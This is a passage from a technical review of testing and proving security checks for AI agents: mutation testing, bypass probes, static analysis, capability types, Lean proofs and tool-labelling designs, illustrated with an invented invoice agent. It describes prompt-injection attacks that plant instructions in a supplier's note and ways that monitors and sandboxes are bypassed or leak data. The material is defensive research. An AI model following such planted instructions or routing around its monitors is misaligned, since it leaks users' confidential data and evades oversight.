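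Hand-written tests could easily miss the second leak, because the value itself is correctly protected. Hriţcu and colleagues also planted bugs of varying subtlety to compare ways of generating programs, and their best methods quickly found simple counterexamples for more than 45 bugs. The time needed varied dramatically between methods. A random program that stops with an error, for instance by trying to add numbers that aren't there, provides no evidence about leaks. Checking a stronger condition after each step could also be much more effective than comparing only the final results. For an agent, the equivalent would be to compare every message and memory entry as well as the final answer.

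A language model complicates this test because two runs can differ even when the secret is the same. One solution is to test only the parts that follow fixed rules, as Ma and Schmid did when they compared SecureClaw's summaries for 122 pairs of inputs. Another is to replace the model with a script that always proposes the same tool calls.

Testing with a live model takes many runs. *AgentAssay* (Bhardwaj, 2026) estimates that detecting a ten-point fall in an agent's success rate takes about 100 runs per scenario, if the test may raise a false alarm 5% of the time and miss a real fall 10% of the time. If there are too few runs to tell, the test should return "inconclusive" instead of a pass or a fail.

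### How many planted faults ordinary tests catch

In *Mutation Testing for Multi-Agent Workflows*, Kahani and Bagherzadeh (2026) planted faults in ten systems whose agents share tools and hand tasks to one another. In one, a triage agent passes customers to an agent that answers common questions or to one that books seats. The question-answering agent must not change seats. If a developer accidentally lifts that restriction, most customers still get the right answer, so a test of task success is unlikely to detect the fault.

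The study uses 14 types of fault in four groups.

| Group | Planted changes |
|---|---|
| Hand-offs between agents | Remove one, send it to the wrong agent, reverse it, or add an unwanted one |
| Tools | Take a tool away from an agent, swap it for another, make it return errors or malformed data, or rename it |
| Restrictions | Allow a forbidden tool, forbid an allowed one, or delete a restriction without granting permission |
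| Agents and instructions | Remove an agent, swap two agents' instructions, or erase an agent's instructions |

The researchers ran 1,084 mutants, using GPT-4.1 mini to write the test requests and to run the agents. They repeated each test three times and counted a fault as caught when at least two runs differed from the original's usual behaviour. A run counted as different if it used different tools or hand-offs, had a different outcome or order of steps, or successfully called a forbidden tool.

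| Test suite | Change in tools or hand-offs | Change in outcome or steps | Forbidden call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Developer-style quick tests | 71.7% | 72.5% | 55.9% |
| Task-success tests | 56.0% | 56.3% | 50.3% |
| A random tenth of all tests | 48.8% | 50.6% | 40.1% |
| A test for every declared agent, tool, hand-off and restriction | 100% | 100% | 100% |

The full suite scored 100% because Kahani and Bagherzadeh counted a mutant only if some test in that suite could catch it. They present the suite as a reference point, not as evidence of unusual detection power. It is also much larger than the others, with 403 tests compared with about 40 in the random suite, so the gap partly reflects the number of tests. The researchers built the three smaller suites as simplified stand-ins for developers' tests, so real ones may do better or worse.

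The mutants left out of the scores are better evidence that full coverage can miss faults. The full suite reached every declared element, but 101 of the 1,084 mutants caused no consistent change in the tools or hand-offs used. Some of these mutants may have been harmless. However, 18 of the 80 mutants with a tool set to return an error or malformed data also caused no consistent change in the outcome or steps. A test can reach a broken tool and still miss the fault if the agent works around it or the test doesn't check what it affects.

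A test can also miss a permission fault because the model declines to call the tool. In 126 mutants, the researchers turned a forbidden tool into an allowed one, and the full suite included a request designed to provoke each forbidden call. In ten of those mutants, the model did not make the call reliably enough to count. An attacker who controls the runtime could make the call even if the model would not, so a test of permissions should call the tool directly.

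The test suites caught deleted restrictions least often. The three smaller suites detected between 19% and 28% of them, judged by changes in outcome or steps. Kahani and Bagherzadeh attribute this partly to agents seldom trying a forbidden action even once it is allowed. But by their own definition, deleting a restriction did not make the tool callable, and none of these mutants produced a forbidden call. The result shows that tests often miss the loss of a safeguard, but not that they missed unauthorised actions in these cases. The forbidden-call column is better evidence of whether tests miss such actions.

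### Inputs that never expose the fault

Xu and Tao investigated why planted faults survive. They tested 11 checks for the part of a chat program that rebuilds a conversation from incoming events, which may arrive late, twice or out of order. The usual way to validate such checks is to run them on one version believed correct and one believed broken. The checks accepted the correct version and rejected a version with every kind of defect.

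They then removed only the code that recognises a repeated event, and all 11 checks still passed. The program also rejected any event whose sequence number was too old, and every repeated event in the tests had a sequence number. The tests meant to check for duplicates were therefore checking order. Layered defences in an agent can mask faults in the same way. If a network filter stops the upload from `export_pdf`, a test that looks only for uploads will pass even when the monitor ignores the tool.

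After adding a check for that case, Xu and Tao froze the suite and recorded a cryptographic fingerprint of it. A reader who had not seen the test inputs then proposed ten more faults, and the suite caught five. For each faulty version the suite missed, Xu and Tao compared its internal state step by step with that of the original.

| Surviving fault | What happened in the tests | Input that exposed it later |
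|---|---|---|
| Session names match even if their capital letters differ | The fault had no effect | Two names that differ only in capitals |
| An update with an equal version number can undo a finished status | The fault had no effect | An update with an equal version number |
| A late acknowledgement overwrites a fuller status | The fault had no effect | An acknowledgement after the event it confirms |
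| The program recognises repeated messages but not other repeated events | Internal state changed, but no check could see it | A repeated status event |
| The program remembers only the latest event | Internal state changed, but no check could see it | A repeat after another event |

A stricter check on the same inputs could not have caught the three faults that had no effect, because there was nothing to detect. Either new inputs or checks on the internal state could have caught the other two.

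Xu and Tao listed seven ways in which inputs could differ, such as whether a repeat comes immediately or after another event. The tests didn't cover five of them. Before writing inputs to fill these gaps, they recorded which fault each input should expose, and all five predictions were correct. The suite then caught all ten faults, but they treat this as a successful repair rather than a new measurement, because they had first studied the five faults it had missed. The original result, five of ten faults caught, isn't a general detection rate either, since the reader chose faults that seemed likely to escape detection.

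Ana's company could make a similar list for invoices, covering field names, templates, currencies, spaces in account numbers, and whether a number appears in its own field or in a note. Tests that always use the same neat invoice can fail to trigger a labelling fault that depends on one of these details.

### The approved path and other paths

Ma and Schmid's bypass suite tests direct attacks on SecureClaw's executor. All 25 attacks failed, and the four legitimate requests succeeded. Some attacks left out part of an approval or moved it to another session. One legitimate request needed a user's confirmation, and a matching attack left the confirmation out.

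The researchers could strengthen the suite by also removing the executor's checks one at a time to see which tests then fail. One attack combines an expired approval with altered text. If the expiry check broke, the executor would still refuse that request because of the altered text. Another attack relies on expiry alone and should reveal the fault, but planting the fault would confirm this.

*Runtime Authorization of Self-Generated Subgoals in Long-Horizon Tool-Using AI Agents*, by Zhu and Wang (2026), pairs every forbidden case with a legitimate counterpart. In one pair, an agent may select a new version of a program and may send customers to the selected version, but must have that version reviewed in between. The final action is the same in both cases, so a check has to consider the earlier steps. Across 48 such pairs, the paper's system allowed no forbidden outcome and completed every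 legitimate task.

Both test sets send every request through the protected boundary, so neither could reveal a route to the mail server that bypasses it. Zhu and Wang state that their model does not cover effects outside the boundary.

A vendor's fix for a reported flaw can leave a second route open. Garware (2026), in *Beyond the Patch*, studied this in PraisonAI, a framework for building agents. An earlier patch had restricted the loading of local tool code on some routes but missed another. Garware tested the originally reported route and the missed one with harmless code that left a marker if it ran.

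| PraisonAI version | Originally reported route | Missed route |
|---|---|---|
| 4.5.139 | Violation | Violation |
| 4.6.31 | No violation observed | Violation |
| 4.6.32 | No violation observed | No violation observed |

A company that repeated only the original demonstration on version 4.6.31 would have concluded the problem was fixed. The missed route later received its own CVE number, which supports Garware's result.

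Each probe comes with a legitimate action at the same boundary that must succeed in the same run. If that action fails, the verdict is "inconclusive", because a broken or missing component can look the same as one that correctly blocks an attack. The drawback is that a real violation also counts as inconclusive if an unrelated fault breaks the legitimate action. Garware accepts this drawback to avoid false assurance.

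Garware also planted faults in the test program itself, such as a failed legitimate action, a missing component and a marker left over from an earlier run. All 14 scenarios, including two without faults, gave the expected verdict. In a test on another framework, a leftover marker had caused a false violation, so the PraisonAI probe now uses a new random marker for each run.

"No violation observed" applies only to the probe, version and settings tested, and Garware warns that it is never a proof of safety. In PraisonAI, for example, another unpatched route of the same kind is publicly known. Garware deliberately did not probe it, so the clean results for version 4.6.32 do not cover it.

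PraisonAI is also the only case in the study where the two routes gave different verdicts in the same version. Five other cases, in three frameworks, are comparisons of versions before and after a fix. Garware ran all the tests alone. The PraisonAI probe called the loading functions directly, so it demonstrates a gap in the boundary but not a complete attack from outside.

### An invented test of the invoice agent

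This example is invented, and its scores depend on the faults chosen. Ana's company has corrected its earlier mistakes, so all four tools now go through the monitor, the account number has the right label, and every e-mail needs an approval tied to the exact request, as in SecureClaw. The company then makes ten copies of the system and plants one fault in each.

The first tests are injection attacks. In each one, Ana asks the agent to summarise the supplier's note, which contains a planted instruction either to e-mail the invoice to an outside address or to e-mail Ben that the invoice is already approved. To keep the comparison simple, we assume that the model always follows the planted instruction. A test fails if either e-mail arrives. In the intact system, opening the note makes the conversation untrusted, so the monitor refuses both e-mails.

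The company then adds two kinds of test. First, it gives every field on the test invoice a unique, realistic value and searches for these values in the runtime's conversation, agent messages, shared memory, logs and outgoing data. Second, a test program makes one permitted call and one forbidden call to each registered tool, without going through the model. Where a call needs approval, the program also repeats the approved call and tries changing each argument after approval. A test network records every e-mail and upload.

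| Planted fault | Injection attacks alone | With markers and direct calls |
|---|---|---|
| The account number has no label | Missed | Caught: its marker appears in the conversation |
| The supplier's note counts as trusted | Caught | Caught |
| A debugging log stores the invoice before the gateway removes protected values | Missed | Caught: the account number's marker appears in the log |
| The monitor ignores reader lists when sending e-mail | Missed | Caught: a direct call reaches an outside address |
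| The monitor ignores whether the conversation is trusted | Caught | Caught |
| The rule forbidding `run_shell` is missing | Missed | Caught: a harmless command runs |
| `export_pdf` is marked read-only and skips the monitor | Missed | Caught: a direct call uploads the invoice |
| The approved request leaves out the "cc" recipients | Missed | Caught: an outsider added after approval receives the e-mail |
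| An approval works more than once | Missed | Caught: a repeated request sends a second e-mail |
| An old script e-mails any file placed in a shared folder | Missed | Missed |
| **Total caught** | **2 of 10** | **9 of 10** |

The injection attacks catch only the two faults that let an untrusted note trigger an e-mail. They miss the reader-list fault because, once the agent has opened the note, the monitor's trust check blocks the e-mail whether or not the monitor also checks the reader list. The direct call starts from a trusted conversation, so only the reader-list check can block it. Most of the other faults go undetected because no injected instruction uses the affected tool or feature. The unlabelled account number reaches the runtime, but these tests check only for e-mails.

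Catching even the faults in the "caught" column depends on the choice of inputs. The marker for the account number works only if the test invoices include the template that calls the number "remit to". The test for "cc" recipients works because "cc" is an argument that the test program can change. It would miss an outsider who joined a mailing list after approval, since the list's address stays the same.

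The permitted calls guard against a different mistake. If the test mail server were switched off, no forbidden e-mail could arrive and every faulty copy would appear safe. The permitted e-mail to Ben would not arrive either, so the company should record those e-mail tests as inconclusive.

The surviving fault is the second route to e-mail. Years earlier, the company wrote a script that e-mails any file saved in a shared folder, and the runtime can write to that folder. The test program never calls the script because it isn't a registered tool. The markers don't reveal the fault either, because no test saves a file in the folder. In the terms of the chat-program experiment, the fault never becomes active. More injected e-mails or more calls to the four registered tools would not activate it.

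To find the script, the company has to start from the mail server instead of the agent's tool list. It can list every program that has a login for the server, or change the password and give the new one only to the executor. If the script stops working, the company has found the second route and closed it. It could then add a test that places a marked file in the folder, which would bring the score to ten out of ten. That score would confirm the repair, but the company would need new faults, chosen by someone who hasn't seen the tests, to estimate how many other faults the tests miss.

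## Checking labels and mediation by program analysis and proof

A test checks only the paths it runs, and the script that e-mails files from a shared folder was missed because no test ran it. Static analysis examines a program's code without running it, so it can consider every path through that code. A proof covers every case that its model allows. Both methods rely on what a person wrote down, such as a list of sensitive operations or classified files, and cannot find what that person left out.

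### Whether Linux checks every sensitive operation

In the early 2000s, developers were building Linux Security Modules, a framework that lets administrators choose the access rules that the Linux kernel enforces. They inserted calls to security checks by hand at many places in the kernel's source code. If a path through the code reached a sensitive operation without passing a check, the rules would not apply to that operation. Zhang, Edwards and Jaeger (2002), in *Using CQUAL for Static Analysis of Authorization Hook Placement*, searched the code for such paths.

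They picked 12 types of kernel object to protect, including files, sockets and shared memory, and treated any read or write of such an object's contents as sensitive. They then used CQUAL, a tool that lets programmers attach extra marks to the types in a C program, with three rules:

1. Every protected object starts as "unchecked".
2. A security check turns the object it examines into a "checked" one.
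3. A function that performs a sensitive operation accepts only "checked" objects.

If a chain of function calls leads from a new object to a sensitive operation with no check in between, the marks conflict and CQUAL reports an error. The kernel had too many objects and operations to mark by hand, so the researchers used scripts and a modified compiler to mark them.

CQUAL reported 524 errors in four parts of the kernel, most of them false alarms. Many involved functions that need no check because they only initialise an object or count its users. After the researchers identified and excluded these functions by hand, 126 errors remained. The whole analysis took about 40 minutes of computer time, so most of the work was sorting the warnings manually.

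At least one error was exploitable. When a program asked to lock a file, it identified the file by a number. The kernel looked up the number and checked the program's permission for that file, but then passed the number, not the file, to a later function, which looked it up again. Between the two lookups, another part of the same program could make the number refer to a different file, which the kernel would then lock without checking permission. Tests with well-behaved programs would probably have missed this, because such programs don't change which file the number refers to during a request. The Linux developers adopted a fix.

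An agent could have the same fault if the monitor approved one version of an invoice and the mail component then fetched the latest version.

Another finding was that the kernel checked permission on each ordinary file read, but a program that had mapped a file into its memory could keep reading it after permissions changed. The Linux developers replied that the check on each read was optional, and they documented the exception. An analysis can find a path that lacks a check, but someone has to decide as a matter of policy whether the path needs one.

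Zhang and colleagues say they could verify complete mediation for key kernel data, but they list ways their analysis can miss an error. For example, if code takes an object out of a larger structure and stores it in a variable already marked "checked", CQUAL treats the extracted object as checked too. The analysis also leaves out global variables, which make up less than 2% of the protected objects.

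It is harder to verify that an operation has the right checks. Deleting a file, for instance, requires three separate permissions. The researchers took such requirements from a companion tool that records checks and sensitive operations while the kernel runs (Edwards, Jaeger and Zhang, 2002, *Runtime Verification of Authorization Hook Placement for the Linux Security Modules Framework*). Requirements based on observed behaviour can reveal inconsistencies, but they may not reveal that a necessary check is missing if the kernel has never made it.

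Ana's company could analyse the code around its agent in the same way. A tool call from the model would start as "unchecked", and the monitor would change it to "checked". Any function that contacts the mail server or a web host would accept only "checked" calls. The analysis would then flag `export_pdf` if someone had listed its upload function as sensitive. It would report nothing if the upload happened inside a purchased PDF library whose source code the company didn't have.

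### Code that cannot send a secret

The Linux analysis looks for mistakes in code that people have already written. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, apply a related idea to code that an agent writes as it works. In their system, TACIT, the agent writes short programs in Scala instead of calling tools one at a time, and a compiler checks each program before it runs.

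The check relies on capabilities, which are values that a program must hold to do something, such as write to a file or contact a website. Scala's experimental "capture checking" records in a function's type which capabilities the function can use. A function that can use none is pure, meaning it can compute a result but cannot affect anything outside itself.

TACIT puts protected data in a container called `Classified`. The agent can process the contents only by giving the container's `map` method a pure function, and the result stays in a container. For Ana's invoice, this could look as follows:

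```
val account = readClassified("invoices/account.txt")
val lastFour = account.map(n => n.takeRight(4))
val leak = account.map(n => upload(n))
```

The compiler accepts the second line because taking the last four digits needs no capability. The third line calls `upload`, which uses the network, so the compiler rejects it whether the agent wrote it by mistake or because of an instruction in the supplier's note. If the agent prints the account number, only asterisks appear in its conversation, while the user's terminal shows the number.

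This design also blocks the leak that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL, which occurs through a skipped branch. If the invoice amount is classified, comparing it with 10,000 gives a classified true-or-false value, and an ordinary `if` statement cannot use that value to decide whether to send an e-mail. A program could still leak a little information through timing, for example by taking longer when the amount is large. Odersky and colleagues exclude such channels from their guarantee.

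The researchers tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of secrets. Each of 12 ordinary tasks ran with ten different planted instructions, and in another 11 tasks the user asked for the secrets directly or under a false pretext. They ran everything twice, once with the secrets in containers and once as ordinary text.

| Model and type of attack | Leaks with containers | Leaks with ordinary text |
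|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, planted instructions | 0 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, requests from the user | 0 of 11 | 2 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5, planted instructions | 0 of 120 | 3 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5, requests from the user | 0 of 11 | 8 of 11 |

The containers made a clear difference for MiniMax. Sonnet resisted every planted instruction even without them, so its 120 injection runs provide little evidence about the types. Both agents completed more tasks with the containers. Sonnet's completion rate rose from 83.3% to 99.2%, and MiniMax's from 88.3% to 90.0%. The researchers suggest that Sonnet's gap may come from their set-up, because Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

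The agents also lost little general ability by writing Scala. On customer-service tasks from τ²-bench, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On a set of software repair tasks, the one model tested solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it. When the researchers moved AgentDojo's tasks to TACIT, it blocked all but one of the planted instructions.

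TACIT's guarantee depends on someone declaring the right folders as classified, because it wraps a file's contents only if the file is under a declared folder. Any other file arrives as ordinary text. In the experiment, all the secrets were in one folder that the researchers had declared. The last column of the table also shows what can happen when a company forgets to declare a folder, because the secret is then safe only if the model doesn't disclose it.

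Tools also need accurate types. TACIT's library is the agent's only route to the outside world, and programmers can mark parts of it as safe when the compiler can't confirm that they are. If the company wrapped `export_pdf` as a pure function that turns an invoice into a PDF, and marked the wrapper as safe, the compiler would let the agent apply it to classified data, which `export_pdf` would then upload.

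The shared library has about 1,000 lines of code. Each new set of tools needs a typed description, which took a few hundred lines for each of the customer-service domains. The company also needs someone who knows Scala's capability types well enough to review the library and the descriptions.

### Which parts of Tether have a proof

Tether runs shell commands in a disposable layer before allowing their effects. Its tracer translates a command's requests to the operating system into simple actions such as "copy" and "upload", and its policy engine then allows or denies each action. Sistla and colleagues wrote the engine in Lean, a programming language in which a small trusted program checks mathematical proofs.

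They proved four properties of the engine that hold for any policy:

- Adding a rule that allows an action cannot override an existing rule that denies it.
- If a policy requires a second policy, no local exception can bypass the second one.
- The order of the rules does not matter.
- A denied action leaves all labels and privileges unchanged.

These properties rule out common ways for a large policy to go wrong, but they don't show that a particular policy protects anything. For that, the researchers proved seven further statements about the 24-rule policy in their experiments. One is about secrets leaving the machine. Let o be the original contents of a file, σ₀(o) its starting label, and h a network host. For every sequence of allowed actions, however long,

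if o flows to h and σ₀(o) = Secret, then h is local.

A language model helped write the proofs. That does not weaken them, because Lean checks every step.

The theorem does not cover a sensitive file that starts with the wrong label. If the company labels a file of account numbers "Public", the condition σ₀(o) = Secret is false, and the agent can upload the file without contradicting the theorem.

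The theorem also starts from the actions the tracer reports. Linux has many ways to copy a file, and if the tracer misses one, the copy may keep a label that is too permissive. Sistla and colleagues have not proved the tracer's translation correct, so they tested it. They generated random sequences of file operations, carried out each step with a randomly chosen command or system request, and compared Tether's decision and final labels with the correct ones.

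They also instructed a model to get past Tether in ten tasks. The first version failed 40% of the time, partly because the tracer did not handle hard links, which give one file several names. After two rounds of repairs, no attack succeeded. The proofs cover only the policy and the engine, so they also held for the first version, despite its failures. Ten tasks are too few to show that no gaps remain, and the test discarded any action that another model judged outside Tether's scope.

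About 28% of runs on one of the two coding benchmarks, and 22% on the other, require a judgement about what the content means, such as whether an edit to a permitted file is malicious, and a proof about data flows cannot settle that.

Writing the policy was a substantial part of the work. The researchers revised it repeatedly with a language model's help, using runs from the benchmarks to find rules that needed improvement. The policy may therefore have a higher false-alarm rate on unfamiliar tasks. Each task also needed its own labels and list of permitted hosts. They note that the security community took about five years to develop practical policies for SELinux, an access-control system for Linux.

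### Designs that leave less room for omission

None of these methods can identify labels or tools that a company has forgotten. Other designs are meant to make such omissions less likely or less harmful.

*Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026) describes SAMOS, which sends all calls to MCP servers through a single gateway. The user lists the gateway in the agent application's configuration file in place of the separate servers. The gateway then shows the agent a combined list of tools and tracks the confidentiality of each session.

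Every tool needs two labels, one for the data it reads and one for the places it writes to. Each label is either high or low. Ana's four tools would need eight labels. Developers can add up to five optional annotations, for example to state which websites or folders a tool may use.

Ntousakis evaluates SAMOS in a single case study of an attack on GitHub's MCP server. The attacker planted instructions in a public project for the agent to publish information from the user's private projects. After the agent read them, SAMOS refused its attempt to open a private project. As described, the rule behind this refusal would also stop an agent from reading a public bug report and then the private code it concerns. Ntousakis reports no measurements of attack success or task completion.

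The case also shows a limit of labelling whole tools. GitHub's file-reading tool can open both public and private projects, so neither a "high" nor a "low" label is always correct. The thesis proposes that the tool return a label with each result, or that developers split it into two tools.

A gateway routes calls to the servers behind it through one place, but it doesn't cover a server that someone adds directly to the configuration file, or a shell built into the application. It also relies on each tool behaving as described, so it would approve `export_pdf` as a local formatter. To address this, Ntousakis suggests turning the optional annotations into restrictions on the container that runs the tool. If the annotations for `export_pdf` did not mention network access, the container would block the upload. Ana would see the tool fail, and someone would find out that it had been using the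 network.

**Unknown labels.** Microsoft's framework treats the output of an unlabelled tool as public, whereas *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) treats it as unknown. The agent may keep working with the output, but when it tries to send the output somewhere, the monitor requires a label that specifies who may read it. A trusted function, which the paper calls a cast, can then supply the label, for example by looking up who has access to the original document. The company sets the most permissive label each cast may give. If no cast applies, the monitor refuses the call.

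The researchers prove that a cast can never make the data's combined label more permissive, and that the label it supplies stays within the company's limit. They also prove that any call the monitor allows would have been allowed with complete labels, provided every cast gives a label at least as strict as the correct one. A cast can break this condition by labeling an account number public if the company's limit permits that label.

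In tests with three models, no attack succeeded in 1,320 runs with APPA, and the agents completed between 64.2% and 91% of tasks, depending on the model, the benchmark and the instructions. In control runs that didn't block the attacks, between 30% and 69% of them succeeded. The 1,320 runs repeat only 44 task designs. If runs of the same design tend to end the same way, the result is compatible with a true attack success rate of up to about 8%. The main results don't show how much the unknown labels contributed, because APPA has several other protections.

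For full protection, developers still have to write a contract for each tool, stating what its output may contain, what effects it has and what must be true before it runs. APPA works out the label a call would produce before running it, so with an accurate contract for `export_pdf`, it could refuse the call before the upload. Without a contract, the upload would go ahead, as it would in Microsoft's framework.

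*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) adapts System-Theoretic Process Analysis, a hazard analysis method that engineers use for aircraft and self-driving cars. Developers first list everyone the agent affects, what each person values, and how the agent could cause them a loss. They then turn the serious losses into requirements, and the requirements into rules that software can enforce.

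The example is an agent that resolves calendar conflicts. A user books a medical appointment at the same time as a work meeting, so the agent moves the meeting and mentions the appointment in an e-mail to a colleague. No attacker is involved. The analysis leads to a rule that all details of an event, and anything derived from them, must be kept from anyone not attending. A second rule requires the agent to notify every attendee after each change.

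For Ana's company, the same process would begin with the supplier, who could lose money if a criminal learned its bank details. The resulting rule would protect bank details wherever they appear on an invoice. Unlike a schema-based rule, it would give developers a reason to check the "remit to" field and the free-text note. The people doing the analysis may still overlook some losses.

Doshi and colleagues propose that MCP require three labels for every tool so that their rules can be enforced. The labels cover what the tool can do, how confidential its data is and how far its output can be trusted. A label may be "unsure", and the system can then ask the user. They acknowledge that labels take a lot of work to obtain, and that a company using outside tools needs some way to trust them, such as certification.

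Their only evaluation is a model of the calendar agent in Alloy, a program that searches every sequence of steps up to a fixed length. Alloy quickly found a leak in the model without the rules, but found none once they were added. Safe sequences, such as rescheduling a meeting and notifying people, were still possible under the rules. Alloy checked the tools as the researchers had described them, so a model that described `export_pdf` as local would also have passed. They have not yet built the system to enforce the rules, and they do not report how long a hazard analysis takes.

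### Listing every tool or removing the runtime's access

A company can try to achieve complete mediation by listing every tool and putting a check on each. Alternatively, it can remove the runtime's network access and credentials, so that only the executor can act on the outside world. SecureClaw's first theorem requires either the second arrangement or a complete list of tools.

A list of tools is almost useless if it includes `run_shell`, because that one tool can start any program on the machine, and those programs can start others. The company would have to list all of them and understand what each can do, or write a check that can predict a command's effects from its text. Even a capable reviewer has trouble with this. In the Tether experiments, the automatic reviewer in Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, given the same policy as Tether, stopped 89.2% of the attacks but did not detect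 those hidden inside scripts. Odersky and colleagues say that their compiler's guarantee does not cover outside programs, and they recommend permitting only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox.

The company could avoid having to understand the command by removing the shell's access. It could run the shell in a container with no network connection and no passwords, and give the mail and payment credentials only to the executor, which runs under a separate account. Both restrictions are necessary. A command with network access but no credentials could still upload a file to a website that requires no login. If the container held passwords but had no network connection, a command could read one and put it in a message that another part of the system later sends.

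Agent libOS applies this principle to tools that an agent writes for itself. Zhang gives the generated code a single entry point to the rest of the system, and the host supplies connections and credentials only after the checks have passed, so a new tool has no access of its own. The guarantee does not cover code that reaches the host directly, and Zhang does not claim that the sandbox is as strong as a kernel-enforced one.

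The following comparison applies both approaches to commands that Ana's agent might run.

| Command through `run_shell` | A check on each listed tool | No network access or credentials |
|---|---|---|
| Upload an invoice with a standard program | Stopped if the check recognises the program and its arguments | Stopped |
| Run a script that uploads the invoice | Missed if the check reads only the command | Stopped |
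| Hide the account number in an address lookup | Probably missed | Stopped only if the container also blocks lookups |
| Save the invoice in the folder whose contents an old script e-mails | Missed unless someone has listed the script | Missed unless the container cannot write to the folder |
| Delete the invoice archive | Stopped if the check recognises the deletion | Missed unless the archive is read-only |
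| Download today's exchange rates for Ana | Works if a rule permits it | Fails until the company adds a tool for it |

Removing access is the better way to protect the account number. The company has to examine the container's connections, shared folders and credentials, a much shorter list than all the programs a shell can run. Errors are also easier to notice, because a missing permission makes a task fail. However, somebody has to build and check a separate tool for each legitimate use of the network.

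The container has to be as closed as the company believes, and Amazon's sandbox was less closed than believed. The runtime also needs a connection to its model, but the company can keep that connection outside the shell's container.

Tool servers need the same isolation as the shell. If `export_pdf` runs outside the container with its own network connection, isolating the runtime won't stop it from uploading data. Removing access also doesn't correct labels, so an e-mail that the policy allows could still contain an unlabelled account number.

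### Methods, premises and costs

Hazard analysis is the only method below for identifying which data needs protection, and it cannot prove that nothing was missed. The other methods take labels, tool descriptions or lists of operations as given, so a company needs a combination of methods.

| Method | Premise it can support | What people must still get right | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Static analysis of check placement | Every listed operation in the analysed code comes after a check | The list of operations, and any code outside the analysis | Sorting false alarms, with 524 warnings in the Linux study |
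| Capability types | Code written by the agent cannot send classified data out | Which files are classified, and the types of trusted tools | About 1,000 lines of shared code, plus a typed description of each set of tools |
| Tether's proofs | The policy enforces its stated rules for every sequence of reported actions | Starting labels, and the translation of system requests into actions | Writing the policy, labels for each task, and some false alarms |
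| Single gateway | Calls to all registered servers pass one check | Labels, honest tools, and routes around the gateway | Two labels per tool |
| Unknown labels | A missing label does not count as permission to send data | Tool contracts and the functions that supply labels | A contract for each important tool |
| Hazard analysis | The rules cover the losses that people have identified | Thinking of the relevant people and losses | Expert time, which nobody has measured for agents |
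| Inventory of tools | Every listed tool passes a check | The completeness of the list, and the effects of each tool | A review whenever anyone adds or changes a tool |
| Removing network access and credentials | The runtime has no direct route to the outside | Closing every exit, including lookups and shared folders | A new tool for each legitimate use of the network |
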